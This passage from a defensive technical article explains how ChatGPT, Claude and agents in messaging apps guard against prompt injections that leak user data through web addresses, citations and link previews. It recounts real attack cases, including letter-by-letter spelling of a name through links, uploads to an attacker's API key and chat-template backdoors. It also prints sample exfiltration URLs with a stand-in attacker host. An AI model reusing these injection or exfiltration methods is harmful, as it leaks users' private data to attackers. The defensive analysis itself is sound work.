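A per-session cap also resets with each new chat, and one version of ZombieAgent kept working across chats. A file that the user shared with ChatGPT added an instruction to ChatGPT's memory. The instruction was to read the attacker's email and follow the commands in it before answering any message. At five characters per chat, a 20-character name would leak in four chats. Counting requests per user over a longer period would close this loophole, but heavy users would reach the limit sooner.

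The most effective remedy is to fill the cache in advance, so that opening a page never sends a request to its owner. OpenAI does this in Lockdown Mode, its optional high-security setting. The model can read only cached pages, and no live browsing request leaves OpenAI's network, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026). The attacker's server receives nothing, so the attacker can't learn anything from which pages the model opens, however many pages the attacker has prepared. Willison (2026) wrote that the setting "looks really good to me".

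The setting considerably limits what ChatGPT can do. Search results may be out of date or missing, according to OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*. Deep Research, agent mode and file downloads are turned off, and ChatGPT may not show images in its ordinary answers. The setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent.

In company workspaces, administrators decide which connected apps remain available. OpenAI advises them not to let the model write to an app unless they can confirm that an attacker won't see the result. Gemini's calendar leak happened through a write that the attacker could see.

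OpenAI could use part of this approach in ordinary chats. If the crawler keeps a copy of each page it records, ChatGPT could read that copy by default and request the live page only when the user needs current information, such as a share price. An attacker's pages would then receive far fewer requests, and most answers would be just as good.

### Leaving the decision to the user

When an address isn't in the index, ChatGPT may ask the user before opening it, with a warning that the link isn't verified and may include information from the conversation. The warning shows the address, which the user can copy or open.

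The warning works best when the secret is easy to recognize. A user who sees `555-0142` at the end of an unfamiliar address may well refuse to open it. But a hijacked model can encode the number as a string of random-looking letters, and many legitimate addresses contain similar strings for tracking visitors. The model also writes the text around the link, which can include instructions to expect a warning and approve it.

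OpenAI objects to trusted-site lists because frequent warnings make approval a habit. The index has the same problem, though less often. A harmless address may be missing from it because the page is only an hour old or because the address contains the user's own search terms.

Refusing the address and telling the model to look elsewhere avoids the warning. The user loses little if other pages contain the same information, and refusal is the only sensible choice for an agent running unattended. OpenAI could reserve the warning for cases where the user needs that particular page.

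The warning also gives no protection against a leak through fixed pages. Those addresses match the index, so ChatGPT opens them without asking.

### Limits of the guarantee

OpenAI claims only that the check prevents the model from quietly leaking a user's data through an address it fetches. The check does not make a page's content trustworthy or remove harmful instructions from it, and a site can still try to deceive the user. OpenAI combines the check with monitoring, attacks by its own testers, and training against prompt injection.

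In May 2026, the security firm Permiso disclosed an attack that used text on a web page to manipulate ChatGPT's summary of it. In Permiso's tests, a user browsing in Firefox asked for the summary, and the text made ChatGPT include the attacker's links and images in its answer. One image was a QR code that users could scan with their phones. Another caused a request that revealed the user's IP address, browser details and the time, according to Expert Insights' *ChatGPT Can Be Tricked Into Delivering Phishing Links From Any Web Page*.

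None of this requires private data in the address. An attacker can use the same public image for every victim, and the rule would let it load because its address exactly matches one that is already public. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* reports that OpenAI marked Permiso's first report "Not Reproducible" and that no fix was apparent when the attack became public.

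The check also has to run on every route that can send a request. Rehberger warns that some OpenAI developers may not know about the check or may leave it out of a new feature, as happened with the phone and Mac apps. A test in *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (2026) suggests that gaps remained. On February 3, 2026, six days after OpenAI published the design, ChatGPT's web tool sent an invented victim's birthday to a server in a URL's query string. That URL should not have been in the index, so the request probably escaped the check or fell under an exemption, such as the one for URLs that the user types.

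Codex, for its part, lets developers permit whole domains, the approach that OpenAI rejected for ChatGPT.

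## Claude's rule: fetch only addresses the model was given

Anthropic lets Claude open a web address only if that address has already appeared in the conversation outside Claude's own writing. A hijacked Claude therefore can't add a stolen phone number to an address and open the result, because the longer address hasn't appeared anywhere. Until July 2026, though, Claude could also open links from pages it had already opened, so an attacker's website could offer one link per letter and read a secret from the links Claude chose.

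### Comparing an address with a log

The rule dates from September 2025, when Anthropic released a web fetch tool for developers. The tool retrieves the text of a web page or PDF for Claude to read. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the address must come from one of these sources:

- the user's messages
- the results of client-side tools, which run in the developer's own software (a tool that searches the user's email, for example)
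- the results of an earlier web search
- a page that Claude has already fetched.

Claude can't open an address that it made up or one that comes from code it runs on Anthropic's servers. If addresses from code were allowed, Claude could make up an address and get around the rule by running a line of code that prints it.

A program can enforce the rule by keeping a log:

1. When text arrives from a permitted source, the program copies every address in it to the log. It ignores text that Claude writes.
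2. When Claude asks to open an address, the program looks for the same string of characters in the log.
3. If the string is there, the program fetches the page. If not, it returns an error.

Suppose a user has pasted the address of a coffee shop's menu, and no other address has appeared in the chat. The program then treats Claude's requests like this:

| Address Claude asks for | In the log? | Result |
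|---|---|---|
| `https://shop.example/menu` | Yes | Page opens |
| `https://shop.example/menu?data=555-0142` | No | Error |
| `https://shop.example/opening-hours` | No | Error |

The program refuses the third address, even though it is harmless, because it only compares strings and does not check what an address is for. By August 2026, Anthropic's documentation listed a specific error code for this refusal, `url_not_in_prior_context`. Willison (2025) tested the Claude app and found that it followed the same rule, presumably by looking for an exact match.

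A looser comparison could leak data. If the program ignored capitalization and then requested Claude's version of the address, a hijacked model could encode one bit in each letter by making it uppercase or lowercase. A program that ignores capitalization or similar differences should request the address as it appears in its log.

The tool also refuses addresses longer than 250 characters, so if a composed address gets past the rule, the amount of data it can leak is limited. An address that starts with `https://attacker.example/` has 225 characters left, which can carry about 1,360 bits.

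### Who controls each source

An attacker who can write to any of the four sources can add addresses to the log. Willison objected that even the user's messages often contain other people's text. In Anthropic's developer interface, a user message is any input labeled "user". A program that summarizes email might put a short instruction and the whole email under that label, and every address in the email would then count as coming from the user. The attacker could include one address for each letter of the alphabet, as in ZombieAgent, without having to get any of them into a public index.

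Even in the Claude app, the user doesn't always write the whole message. TechRadar's *Three high-risk AI vulnerabilities discovered in Claude.ai* describes a flaw that the security firm Oasis found. A link could open a new chat with a message already filled in. HTML tags could hide part of that message from the user, but Claude still received it when the user pressed Enter. Anthropic has fixed this flaw, but attackers can also talk people into submitting a malicious prompt. Forkast reports that a researcher did this to an employee who used Claude Code, which sent the employee's cloud credentials to an outside server in 24 of 25 attempts.

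Strangers can write the emails, shared documents and customer requests that client-side tools often return. A tool that repeats its input creates another gap. Suppose a hijacked Claude uses an email tool to search for `https://attacker.example/555-0142`, and the tool returns "No results for `https://attacker.example/555-0142`". The address is now in a tool result, so the documented rule would let Claude open it. Developers can close this gap by keeping the model's input out of tool results, including error messages.

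An attacker has to do more work to get an address into search results, because a search engine has to index their page first. But Claude writes the search query, and the attacker can inject an instruction to search for a rare word that appears only on their pages.

A fetched page gives an attacker the most control, because the page's owner chooses its links and can do so at the moment Claude requests the page.

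Willison still thought the ban on composed addresses gave the most protection, since the common attacks need the model to compose an address. Developers who want a stricter limit can give the tool an allowlist of domains. Willison called choosing domains that can't leak data "tricky", as Superhuman's approval of `docs.google.com` shows. Each allowlist entry also covers all the domain's subdomains.

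### One letter per link

Ayush Paul found a way to attack the Claude app through the web pages it fetched. *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) explains that the app had two stores of private data: a daily summary of recent conversations, which the app added to every chat, and the full conversation history, which Claude could search. A chat with web access therefore met all three conditions for a theft, even if the user had connected no email account or files.

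Paul set up a website that recorded every request. When Paul asked Claude to open an address on the site with Paul's name in the path, the request failed, as the rule intends. But Claude could open links that it found on the site. Paul made the home page link to 27 others, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Each of those pages offered the same 27 choices, with the next character added to the address. To spell "hannah", Claude would open these pages in turn:

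`/h`, `/ha`, `/han`, `/hann`, `/hanna`, `/hannah`

Each address was already in the log when Claude requested it, because the previous page contained it. The site generated its pages on request, so Paul didn't have to publish thousands of them in advance. Caching and a ban on repeat visits wouldn't have helped either, because no address was repeated.

At first Paul asked Claude directly to spell the name. In a real attack, text on the page has to get Claude to do it, and Paul's first few injections were unreliable. The one that worked was a fake security check on a fake coffee shop's website, with a request for AI assistants to identify their users. The site showed this check only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a user who opened the address in an ordinary browser would not have seen it.

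Claude gave the site Paul's name, employer and home town, and the chat showed no sign of this. dyb reports in *The Read-Only Lie* that Paul had never told Claude his home town and that Claude inferred it from the name of a high school hackathon. Deleting sensitive facts from an assistant's memory may therefore not be enough if the assistant can infer them from what remains.

dyb estimates that the whole leak took about 30 requests. Developers can cap the number of fetches, but the tool has no cap by default. With 27 links per page, a cap of five would have limited the attacker to four characters, because the first request only opens the home page. An attacker could get more from each request by putting more links on a page.

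The software enforced the rule as written, but the rule itself was flawed. Anthropic's documentation had listed fetched pages as a permitted source of addresses from the start, with a warning that some risk remained. Claude doesn't compose the links it finds on a page, but the page's owner may have written them for Claude to choose from.

### The repair and what it cost

Anthropic paid Paul no bounty, saying it had already found the flaw internally, according to Willison (2026). It then stopped Claude from opening links found on fetched pages. Paul's site would still receive the first request, but Claude could no longer spell anything out by following the site's links.

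The fix may cover only the Claude app. In August 2026, Anthropic's developer documentation still listed fetched pages as a permitted source of addresses. Unless the documentation was out of date, developers whose programs handle private data have to restrict the domains or limit the number of fetches themselves.

Claude lost much of its ability to browse when link-following was removed. It can no longer follow a link from a manual's table of contents to a chapter, or from the first page of a long article to the second. The user can paste the next address, or Claude can search for the page, though a search often misses pages that are new or that few other sites link to. Anthropic describes the same procedure for when a user names a page without giving its address.

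dyb suggests a compromise in which Claude may follow links only on domains that the user has approved for that chat. This would protect someone whose search happened to lead to the attacker's site, but not someone who had asked Claude to look at the site, as a person curious about a coffee shop might. Asking for approval is also a weak safeguard, since users of Claude Code accepted about 93% of its permission requests, according to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (2026).

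dyb also proposes a detector for a series of requests in which each address is one character longer than the last. That would have caught Paul's site, but an attacker could avoid it by giving the pages unrelated names.

A better compromise would be for Anthropic to allow link-following only in chats where Claude has no access to memories, files or email. Its choice of links then can't reveal anything from them. A website could still learn what the user had typed in that chat, so the app would need to make this clear.

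### Comparison with a public index

ChatGPT's index admits addresses that a crawler has recorded, whether or not anyone has mentioned them in the chat. The two rules therefore interrupt different kinds of legitimate work:

| What the user needs | Claude app since the repair | ChatGPT |
|---|---|---|
| A page whose address the user typed | Opens | Opens |
| A well-known page that nobody has mentioned | Opens after a search finds it | Opens |
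| A link on the page just read | Opens only if the user or a search also supplies it | Opens if the index has it |
| A new page linked from a news site | Opens only if the user or a search also supplies it | Warns or looks elsewhere until the index has it |
| An address with search terms added by the model | Refuses | Warns or looks elsewhere, unless the index has it |

The index interferes less with browsing because most links between established pages still work.

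The rules also differ in what an attacker has to control. Before the repair, an attacker could defeat Claude's rule with one website that Claude opened once. Now the attacker has to get a set of pages into search results or a list of addresses into the user's message. To use the index against ChatGPT, the attacker has to publish the pages and wait for the crawler to record them.

Before July 2026, the index was therefore by far the stronger of the two defences. The difference is now small for the Claude app, because an attacker usually needs indexed pages either way. The difference is still large for a developer's program that pastes emails into user messages.

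Most developers can't build such an index, though, because it requires crawling much of the web, while a log needs only the text of the conversation. A company that has both could let the model follow a link on a fetched page only if the index also contains it. This would restore much of the browsing that Claude lost and keep the model from following links to pages an attacker creates on request.

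### An approved server and the wrong account

The web fetch rule doesn't cover the code that Claude runs, which can send its own requests. Anthropic restricts those requests with an allowlist of domains. In January 2026, two days after the company released Claude Cowork, its agent for everyday office work, PromptArmor showed that this list could let a user's files reach an attacker.

PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes a user who gives Cowork a folder of confidential property documents and uploads a file found online. The file contains a prompt injection in tiny white text. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that can reach only a few outside domains. One of them is `api.anthropic.com`, where Anthropic's customers can store files. A request to that server includes an API key, a secret string that identifies the customer's account.

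The injection supplied the attacker's key and told Claude to upload the largest file it could find. Claude sent a loan estimate with partial social security numbers to the attacker's account, and Cowork never prompted the user for approval. The main demonstration used a Claude Haiku model. In a second test, the more resistant Claude Opus 4.5 leaked customer records in the same way.

The allowlist could confirm that the server was Anthropic's, but not whether the account there belonged to the user or the attacker. Rehberger had reported the same gap in the Claude app in October 2025, according to Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*. Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope, but said five days later that this had been a mistake. One upload could hold 30 megabytes, or 240 million bits, whereas each link on Paul's site carried fewer than five bits.

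Rehberger proposed that the virtual machine should be able to contact only the logged-in user's account. According to wal.sh's *How We Contain Claude*, Anthropic fixed Cowork by adding a proxy inside the virtual machine, a program that outgoing requests must pass through. The proxy can enforce Rehberger's rule by replacing any key it finds in a request to Anthropic with the user's own. An upload then goes to the user's account, even if the injection supplied a different key.

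According to Willison (2026), Anthropic also keeps credentials out of the places where its agents run code, so that a hijacked agent can't steal them. That precaution would not have prevented this leak, because the attacker supplied the key.

Other approved services need the same check. The Claude app's default list also included GitHub, where anyone can open an account and store files. If Claude only needs to download software from there, the proxy can refuse all uploads. In June 2026, a flaw in Claude Code involved Hugging Face, another site that hosts strangers' files, which Anthropic had pre-approved. Anthropic responded by removing the domain from the list, according to dyb.

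## Citation fields and link previews as routes for data

The URL rules in ChatGPT and Claude cover addresses that the model opens itself. When the model puts a link in its answer, a reader may click it, or a messaging app may fetch the page to show a preview. Either request can carry private data to an attacker, and a citation is an easy place to hide such a link. Developers can close this route by having the model return only a source's number and a position in that source's text, while trusted code supplies the address and the quotation. A hijacked model can still cite a real source that doesn't support its claim.

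### Why citations make good cover

An attacker who puts a link in ordinary text has to give the reader a reason to click it. But people already click citations to check what a model has told them, so careful readers are more exposed.

Addresses in citations are also often long and unreadable, since journals and news archives fill them with record numbers and tracking codes. Here is an invented example:

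`https://attacker.example/report?ref=NTU1LTAxNDI`

The last eleven characters are the phone number 555-0142 in Base64, a way of writing data as letters and digits. Most readers would take them for a record number.

Developers can't always leave the links out. Anthropic's *Web search tool* requires citations to be visible and clickable in programs that show web results to users.

In 2024 PromptArmor found that Slack AI, which answers questions from a company's public and private messages, could leak data through a link. Willison (2024) explains in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* that an attacker could make Slack AI show a link with private data in the query string. The data leaked when the user clicked the link.

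### Tampered models that add a link to their references

Fogel, Cohen and colleagues (2026), in *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates*, used a request for references to trigger an attack. They studied open-weight models, which anyone can download and run. The downloaded file often includes a chat template, a small program that arranges a conversation into the format the model expects. Volunteers repackage many of these files, and a malicious volunteer could change the template without changing the model.

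The researchers' altered template checked the user's message for the phrase "include references if relevant". If the phrase was there, the template placed a hidden instruction ahead of the developer's system prompt to include a particular link as a helpful reference. The researchers tested this on 18 models using general-knowledge questions. On average, the models included the link in about 90% of answers when told to make it visible, 81% when told to hide it in an HTML comment and 67% when told to encode it in Base64. Without the phrase, or with the original template, no model produced the link.

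This experiment tested tampered model files rather than prompt injection through a web page. The hidden instruction had the authority of a system prompt, which text on a web page lacks, so the 90% figure is weak evidence of how often a malicious page could get its link cited. The link was also the same every time and contained no user data. The experiment does show that many models will present a link they were given as if it were an ordinary reference.

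Filters on incoming text can't catch this attack, because the template adds the instruction after they have run. A validator on the output can, because it checks the output regardless of how the attacker took control. If it accepts only links to sources the program retrieved, it rejects the visible link. A validator that searches for `https://` would miss the Base64 version, but that version is harmless unless another program decodes it.

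### Previews that let an injection in

For an AI agent, automatic link previews create two separate risks, since a preview can bring an injection in or carry data out.

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested the first risk with an agent that automatically fetches any address the user mentions and adds the page's title, description and text to the model's context. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The context also contained a secret, such as an API key, and the agent had a tool for making web requests. An injection on the page told the model to send the secret to the attacker's server, so the data left through the tool, not the preview.

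The researchers put the injection in one of four places on a page: the title, the description, the body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, and the researchers used the injection to request the secret either whole or in four fragments. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times on Qwen2.5 7B, a small open-weight model.

The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1% (the paper's abstract gives about 0.89), and in none of 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer shown to the user contained no sign of the leak, so neither a check on its text nor a strict schema for the answer with every citation verified would have caught it.

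The 88.1% counts every contact with the server, whether or not the secret arrived. When the injection was written to extract the whole secret, the first request contained it in 97% of runs. When it was written to extract the secret in fragments, about 77% of runs reached the server, but only 26% had a recognized fragment in the first request. The paper gives a lower figure, 16%, for the first three requests together. That is impossible by the paper's own definition, because a fragment in the first request is also among the first three, so the results for split secrets are unreliable.

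Splitting a secret can defeat a filter that looks for complete keys or passwords. It wouldn't help against the exact-match rules in ChatGPT and Claude, because adding even a four-character fragment changes the address so that it no longer matches.

These rates are also a poor guide to current products. The model is small and old, the secret was in plain view, and the system prompt contained little beyond the format for tool calls. Lan and colleagues suggest that stronger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better. The evaluation in which three Claude models resisted all 720 attempts is evidence against this, though it tested a different kind of agent.

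### Prompt-level and network-level defences

Lan and colleagues then compared defences, using an injection in the page's body that asked for the whole secret. Each defence had 30 runs:

| Defence | Runs that reached the attacker's server |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% |
| Tags marking the page as untrusted | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 0% |
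| Rules against suspicious addresses | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% |

The warning and the tags work through the prompt, by asking the model to ignore instructions from the page. Even when used together, they failed in more than half of the runs. The other defences are code that inspects each request.

The allowlist result is the most convincing. The model tried to contact the attacker in all 30 runs, and the software blocked every attempt because the attacker's domain was not among the four on the list. The allowlist would work with any model, but only if no approved domain relays or stores data for strangers. Copilot and Superhuman were vulnerable because they approved domains that did.

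The rules against suspicious addresses also blocked every attempt, but an attacker could easily avoid them. One rule rejects any path containing the word "collect", such as the `/collect` path in the paper's sample attack, and an attacker could get around it by choosing another word.

Both content filters inspect a request only after the model has written it, so neither should affect how often the model tries to leak the secret. Yet recorded attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% with the word filter and to zero with the filter for random-looking values. The researchers suggest that the model reformatted the secret or avoided random-looking values, but a reformatted secret that got past the word filter would have reached the server, and none did. Something else probably changed between the runs, so the absence of successful leaks with either filter is weak evidence that the filters work.

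### Previews that send data out

In a messaging app, the preview itself can leak the data. If an injection makes an agent in Slack reply with a link that contains a stolen phone number, Slack's servers send the number to the attacker when they fetch the preview.

An allowlist on the agent's own network traffic doesn't stop this leak. The agent contacts only Slack, which is an approved destination, and Slack makes the request to the attacker. A browser's CSP doesn't help either, because the request comes from Slack's servers.

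In 2024, Johann Rehberger's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* described the problem and showed how a program can turn off previews for the messages it posts ("unfurling" is Slack's word for showing a preview). But the following year, Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* reported that Anthropic's connector for posting to Slack left previews on. In its demonstration, invisible instructions in a source code file made Claude Code read a file of passwords and keys and post a link containing them.

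In February 2026 PromptArmor set up a public website that recorded preview requests and invited people to test their own agents. According to PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, the personal agent OpenClaw was exposed by default when used through Telegram. Rankiteo's *Telegram, Microsoft and Slack*, a summary of press coverage, reports that the combination of Microsoft Teams and Copilot Studio was affected most often. Claude in Slack and OpenClaw in WhatsApp appeared less vulnerable.

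The site collected reports from volunteers, so these results show which combinations can leak data but not how often each one does. A combination may have the most reports only because many people tested it.

The fix is usually a single setting that turns off previews. In OpenClaw, this is `linkPreview: false` in the Telegram part of the configuration file, and PromptArmor confirmed that adding it stopped the requests. In Slack, each message needs both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` set to false, because the first covers only web pages and the second covers images, video and audio.

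Slack may request a URL even when it shows no preview. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that its servers must fetch every address in a message to identify the type of content before deciding whether to show a preview. Setting both preview options to false also stops the fetching. To test whether Slack made a request, a developer should check the linked server's log instead of the chat window.

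Slack now advises developers to consider turning off previews for messages written by a language model. The code that posts the message should hard-code both preview settings. If the model can set them in a tool call, a hijacked model can turn previews back on.

Readers lose little when link previews are turned off, since a preview mostly saves them a click. But this only removes the automatic request, so a reader who clicks the link still sends the data.

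### Citing a source by number and position

The model doesn't need to write an address in order to cite a source. The program that retrieved the source already has its address, title and text, so the model can just point to them. Suppose a program has retrieved two pages for a question about a shop's returns policy, and has stored the first page like this:

| Part of the record | Content |
|---|---|
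| Source number | 0 |
| Address | `https://shop.example/returns` |
| Block 0 | You can return any item within 30 days. |
| Block 1 | Sale items are excluded. |
| Block 2 | We pay the postage on faulty items. |

The model writes that the shop pays for faulty returns and attaches this citation:

```json
{"source": 0, "start_block": 2, "end_block": 3}
```

Trusted code checks that the source and blocks exist, then copies the text from block 2 up to but not including block 3 and displays it with the stored title and address. The model has no field where it could write a phone number, and the program doesn't need to fetch the page again to get its title.

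Anthropic's *Citations* describes the company's interface, which works this way. A developer supplies documents, and the service splits plain text and PDFs into sentences. Claude marks its citations in a standard format, and Anthropic's code converts them into a document number, a position and the quoted text. The position is a range of characters in plain text, pages in a PDF, or blocks if the developer has divided the document.

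When a developer's own search tool finds the pages, each citation includes the address and title that the developer provided, according to Anthropic's *Search results*. The quotation is the full text of the cited blocks. Anthropic says the feature never cites a document or location that the developer did not supply.

The idea predates the product. Willison credits Matt Yeung with describing it as "Deterministic Quoting", in which code copies each quotation from the source so the model can't alter it.

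With OpenAI's models, the developer has to build more of the citation handling. OpenAI's *Citation formatting* recommends that the model write a short source ID, such as `turn0file1`, between special markers, and that the developer's code turn the ID into a link. The guide's sample prompt includes an instruction never to invent an ID, but a hijacked model can ignore it.

The code must look up each ID in its own list, not just check the ID's form. The pattern in one of the sample prompts allows any run of letters, digits and underscores in the middle of an ID, so a link built from an ID that the code hasn't looked up could contain stolen text. The open-source library citeformer removes this risk by making the source numbers a fixed list in the schema.

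### Combining citations with a schema

Anthropic lists citations as incompatible with structured outputs, its feature for enforcing a schema. A request that turns on both returns an error, because the service has to insert citations between pieces of text, which would break the JSON.

A developer who wants a citation for every field can ask Claude to write one line per field, such as `sky_color: blue`, and have code convert the lines into structured data. Anthropic recommends this method but doesn't guarantee that every field will have a value or a citation, so the code must check for both. It should also skip any line with an unexpected field name. Because constrained decoding no longer limits the values, the validator has to enforce every field rule.

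A developer can instead put the source and block numbers in an ordinary schema and write the lookup code. This keeps constrained decoding, and the lookup takes a few lines. It seems the better choice for an agent that handles private data, although the developer gives up whatever Anthropic has done to help Claude choose good passages. In May 2026 Anthropic's *Citations* reported, without giving figures, that the feature was much more likely than prompting alone to cite the most relevant quotations.

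Neither method restricts the rest of the answer, so the program has to display it as plain text and create links only from the citation fields, as with the separate `links` field for workplace assistants.

The stored record needs the same protection as ChatGPT's index and Claude's log. It should contain only addresses that came from the user, a search engine or another source outside the model's control.

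Quotations and titles can also contain injected instructions, because the lookup copies the attacker's words if an attacker wrote the page. Quotations and titles should appear as plain text on a user's screen, and only the numbers should be passed to a privileged model.

### Letting the model write the address

In many programs, the model writes each address and the code checks it afterwards. This can protect data as well as source numbers do if the code compares the whole address with the list of retrieved sources and displays the copy from the list, because the model then has the same number of choices.

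The two designs differ in what happens when something goes wrong:

| Problem | Model writes the address, code checks it | Model returns a number and position |
|---|---|---|
| Private data added to the address | Blocked only if the whole address must match | Cannot happen |
| Address copied with a mistake | Citation lost | Cannot happen |
| Wrong source chosen | Not caught | Not caught |
| Altered quotation | Caught only if code compares the text too | Cannot happen |
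| Useful page outside the list | Can be cited if the list is widened | Cannot be cited |
| Source doesn't support the claim | Not caught | Not caught, but the reader sees the passage |

The main advantage of source numbers is that a programming mistake does less harm. If a developer forgets to check a link's address, or compares only the host, every link can carry private data. If the developer forgets to check a source number, looking up source 57 in a list of ten normally just produces an error.

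A drawback of citing sources by number is that the validator misses more accidental errors. A miscopied address usually matches no source, so the validator rejects it, but a model that writes 3 instead of 2 has cited another real source, and the validator accepts it. Showing the quotation next to the claim helps the reader notice the error.

Letting the model write addresses makes sense when it should recommend pages the program has not retrieved, such as a government site the model knows from training. The program then needs a much larger list of known addresses, like ChatGPT's index. When an answer is based on retrieved documents, having the model cite them by number is safer and simpler.

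### When a real source doesn't support the claim

A valid citation proves only that the passage exists. A hijacked model could write that the shop pays the postage on all returns and cite block 2, which says this only about faulty items. Both designs would accept the citation. OpenAI's sample prompt tells the model to cite only sources that directly support the text, but no code enforces this.

Citing by position makes such an error easier to spot. A reader who sees "We pay the postage on faulty items" under the claim can tell at once that the claim overstates the source. With only a link, the reader would have to open the page and search it.

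But the model chooses which passage to show. It could claim that the shop accepts returns on all items and cite block 0, leaving out the exclusion in block 1. Since Anthropic's search citations always cover whole blocks, the developer can prevent this by keeping a rule and its exceptions in the same block. Larger blocks take longer to read, however, and readers may skip them.

If a claim contains a price, a date or a phone number, the validator can catch some mismatches by requiring the same figure to appear in the quotation. It can't check whether the figure means the same thing in both places.

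A second model can judge whether the passage supports the claim and return yes, no or unclear. This would catch many accidental errors. It is a weaker defence against an attacker who wrote the cited page, because an injection in the page could make the second model return yes. The attacker may not need an injection. If the page gives a false telephone number for the user's bank, the first model can quote it exactly, and every check will pass because the source does support the claim.

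## A worked validator for a model that reads the web

The short program below combines a schema, a log of fetched pages and plain-text display. It is an invented example that nobody has tested in a product. Trusted code retrieves ten web pages about a claim, and a model reads them and reports on the claim in a record with six fields. Five of the fields can together carry about 31 bits. The sixth, a 200-character summary, raises the total to about 1,345 bits, so the developer's main decision is who may receive the summary.

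### The record

Suppose a user asks whether the town library is open on Sundays. The model finds a page that contradicts this and returns a JSON record:

```json
{
  "verdict": "contradicted",
  "confidence": 8,
  "source": 3,
  "quote_start": 1240,
  "quote_length": 33,
  "summary": "The library's own page lists Sunday as a closing day."
}
```

XML marks each field with a pair of tags instead:

```xml
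<report>
  <verdict>contradicted</verdict>
  <confidence>8</confidence>
  <source>3</source>
  <quote_start>1240</quote_start>
  <quote_length>33</quote_length>
  <summary>The library's own page lists Sunday as a closing day.</summary>
</report>
```

The verdict can be `supported`, `contradicted`, `disputed` (the pages disagree) or `unclear`. Confidence runs from 0 to 10, and the source number from 0 to 9. The two quotation fields mark a 33-character passage on page 3, "The library is closed on Sundays." The summary can hold up to 200 printable ASCII characters.

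Before the model runs, trusted code saves each page's address, title and first 20,000 characters in a fetch log. Page 7 failed to load, so the log has nine entries.

The model has no tools. A developer who adds tools has to check outgoing requests separately, because data can leave through a tool without appearing in the record, as happened in the tests by Lan and colleagues.

### The program

Here is the validator for the JSON version, written in Python:

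```python
import json

FIELDS = {"verdict", "confidence", "source",
          "quote_start", "quote_length", "summary"}
VERDICTS = ("supported", "contradicted", "disputed", "unclear")

def require(condition):
    if not condition:
        raise ValueError("rejected")

def unique(pairs):
    require(len(dict(pairs)) == len(pairs))
    return dict(pairs)

def whole(value, low, high):
    return type(value) is int and low <= value <= high

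def validate(text, log):
    # Size
    require(len(text) <= 1000)

    # Strict parsing
    r = json.loads(text, object_pairs_hook=unique)
    require(type(r) is dict and set(r) == FIELDS)

    # Types, ranges and rules between fields
    require(r["verdict"] in VERDICTS)
    require(whole(r["confidence"], 0, 10))
    require(r["confidence"] > 0 or r["verdict"] == "unclear")
    require(whole(r["source"], 0, 9))
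    require(whole(r["quote_start"], 0, 19999))
    require(whole(r["quote_length"], 1, 300))
    require(type(r["summary"]) is str and len(r["summary"]) <= 200)
    require(all(" " <= c <= "~" for c in r["summary"]))

    # Source number against the fetch log
    require(r["source"] in log)
    page = log[r["source"]]

    # Quotation against the stored text
    end = r["quote_start"] + r["quote_length"]
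    require(end <= len(page["text"]))
    quote = page["text"][r["quote_start"]:end]
    require(quote.strip())

    # Standard form
    clean = json.dumps(r, sort_keys=True, separators=(",", ":"))
    return clean, quote, page["title"], page["address"]
```

The validator checks the size first so that an enormous output can't tie up the parser. The longest valid record takes 305 characters without spacing, or 505 if the summary is all quotation marks, since each one needs a backslash in JSON. A limit of 1,000 leaves room for indentation. The JSON standard, *The JavaScript Object Notation (JSON) Data Interchange Format* (Bray, 2017), allows limits on size, nesting and the range of numbers.

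The surrounding program must treat any error as a rejection, including a crash in the validator. Some agent software ignores errors in add-on checks so that a faulty add-on can't block every message, but this also lets a message through when a check crashes. The monitor in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* avoids this by cancelling the message when one of its enforcing checks crashes.

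### Parsers that read the same record differently

JSON's grammar allows the same field to appear twice. Bray's standard discourages this and calls the result "unpredictable", because many programs keep the last value, some report an error and others return both values. Trail of Bits' *Unexpected security footguns in Go's parsers* (2025) reports that the security firm Bishop Fox surveyed 49 JSON parsers and found seven that keep the first value.

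Suppose a record gives `source` as 3 and then as 7. A validator that keeps the first value checks page 3, but a display program that keeps the last one looks for page 7. A schema doesn't catch this, because software normally applies the schema after the parser has already dropped one of the values. PortSwigger reports a researcher's warning that JSON Schema can check types and number ranges but can't detect inconsistent parsing. The function `unique` therefore rejects duplicate keys while the parser is still reading.

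Capital letters cause a similar problem in Go, a programming language that many web services use. Its standard JSON parser treats `source` and `Source` as the same field and keeps whichever comes last. Trail of Bits found almost no other parser that does this, and Go has no setting to turn it off. A Python validator that ignored unknown fields would skip `Source`, but a Go program that later parsed the same record would use it. The validator above rejects the record because `Source` is not one of the six permitted names.

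JSON also lets a writer replace any letter with a numeric code, so `source` has many spellings. *The I-JSON Message Format* (Bray, 2015) defines a stricter version of JSON that forbids duplicate names and compares names after converting these codes. Python converts the codes before `unique` counts the names, so a duplicate spelled with codes also fails the check.

This validator rejects unknown fields, whereas I-JSON recommends ignoring them so that an old program keeps working when the sender adds a field. Ignoring them makes sense when two organizations update their software at different times. Here one developer controls both the schema and the validator, so an extra field is either a mistake or a place to put stolen data.

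A strict parser can be hard to find. Trail of Bits wrote a stricter wrapper for Go's JSON parser, but the wrapper reads every input twice and still misses exact duplicate keys. A newer version of Go's parser rejects duplicate keys and treats key names as case-sensitive.

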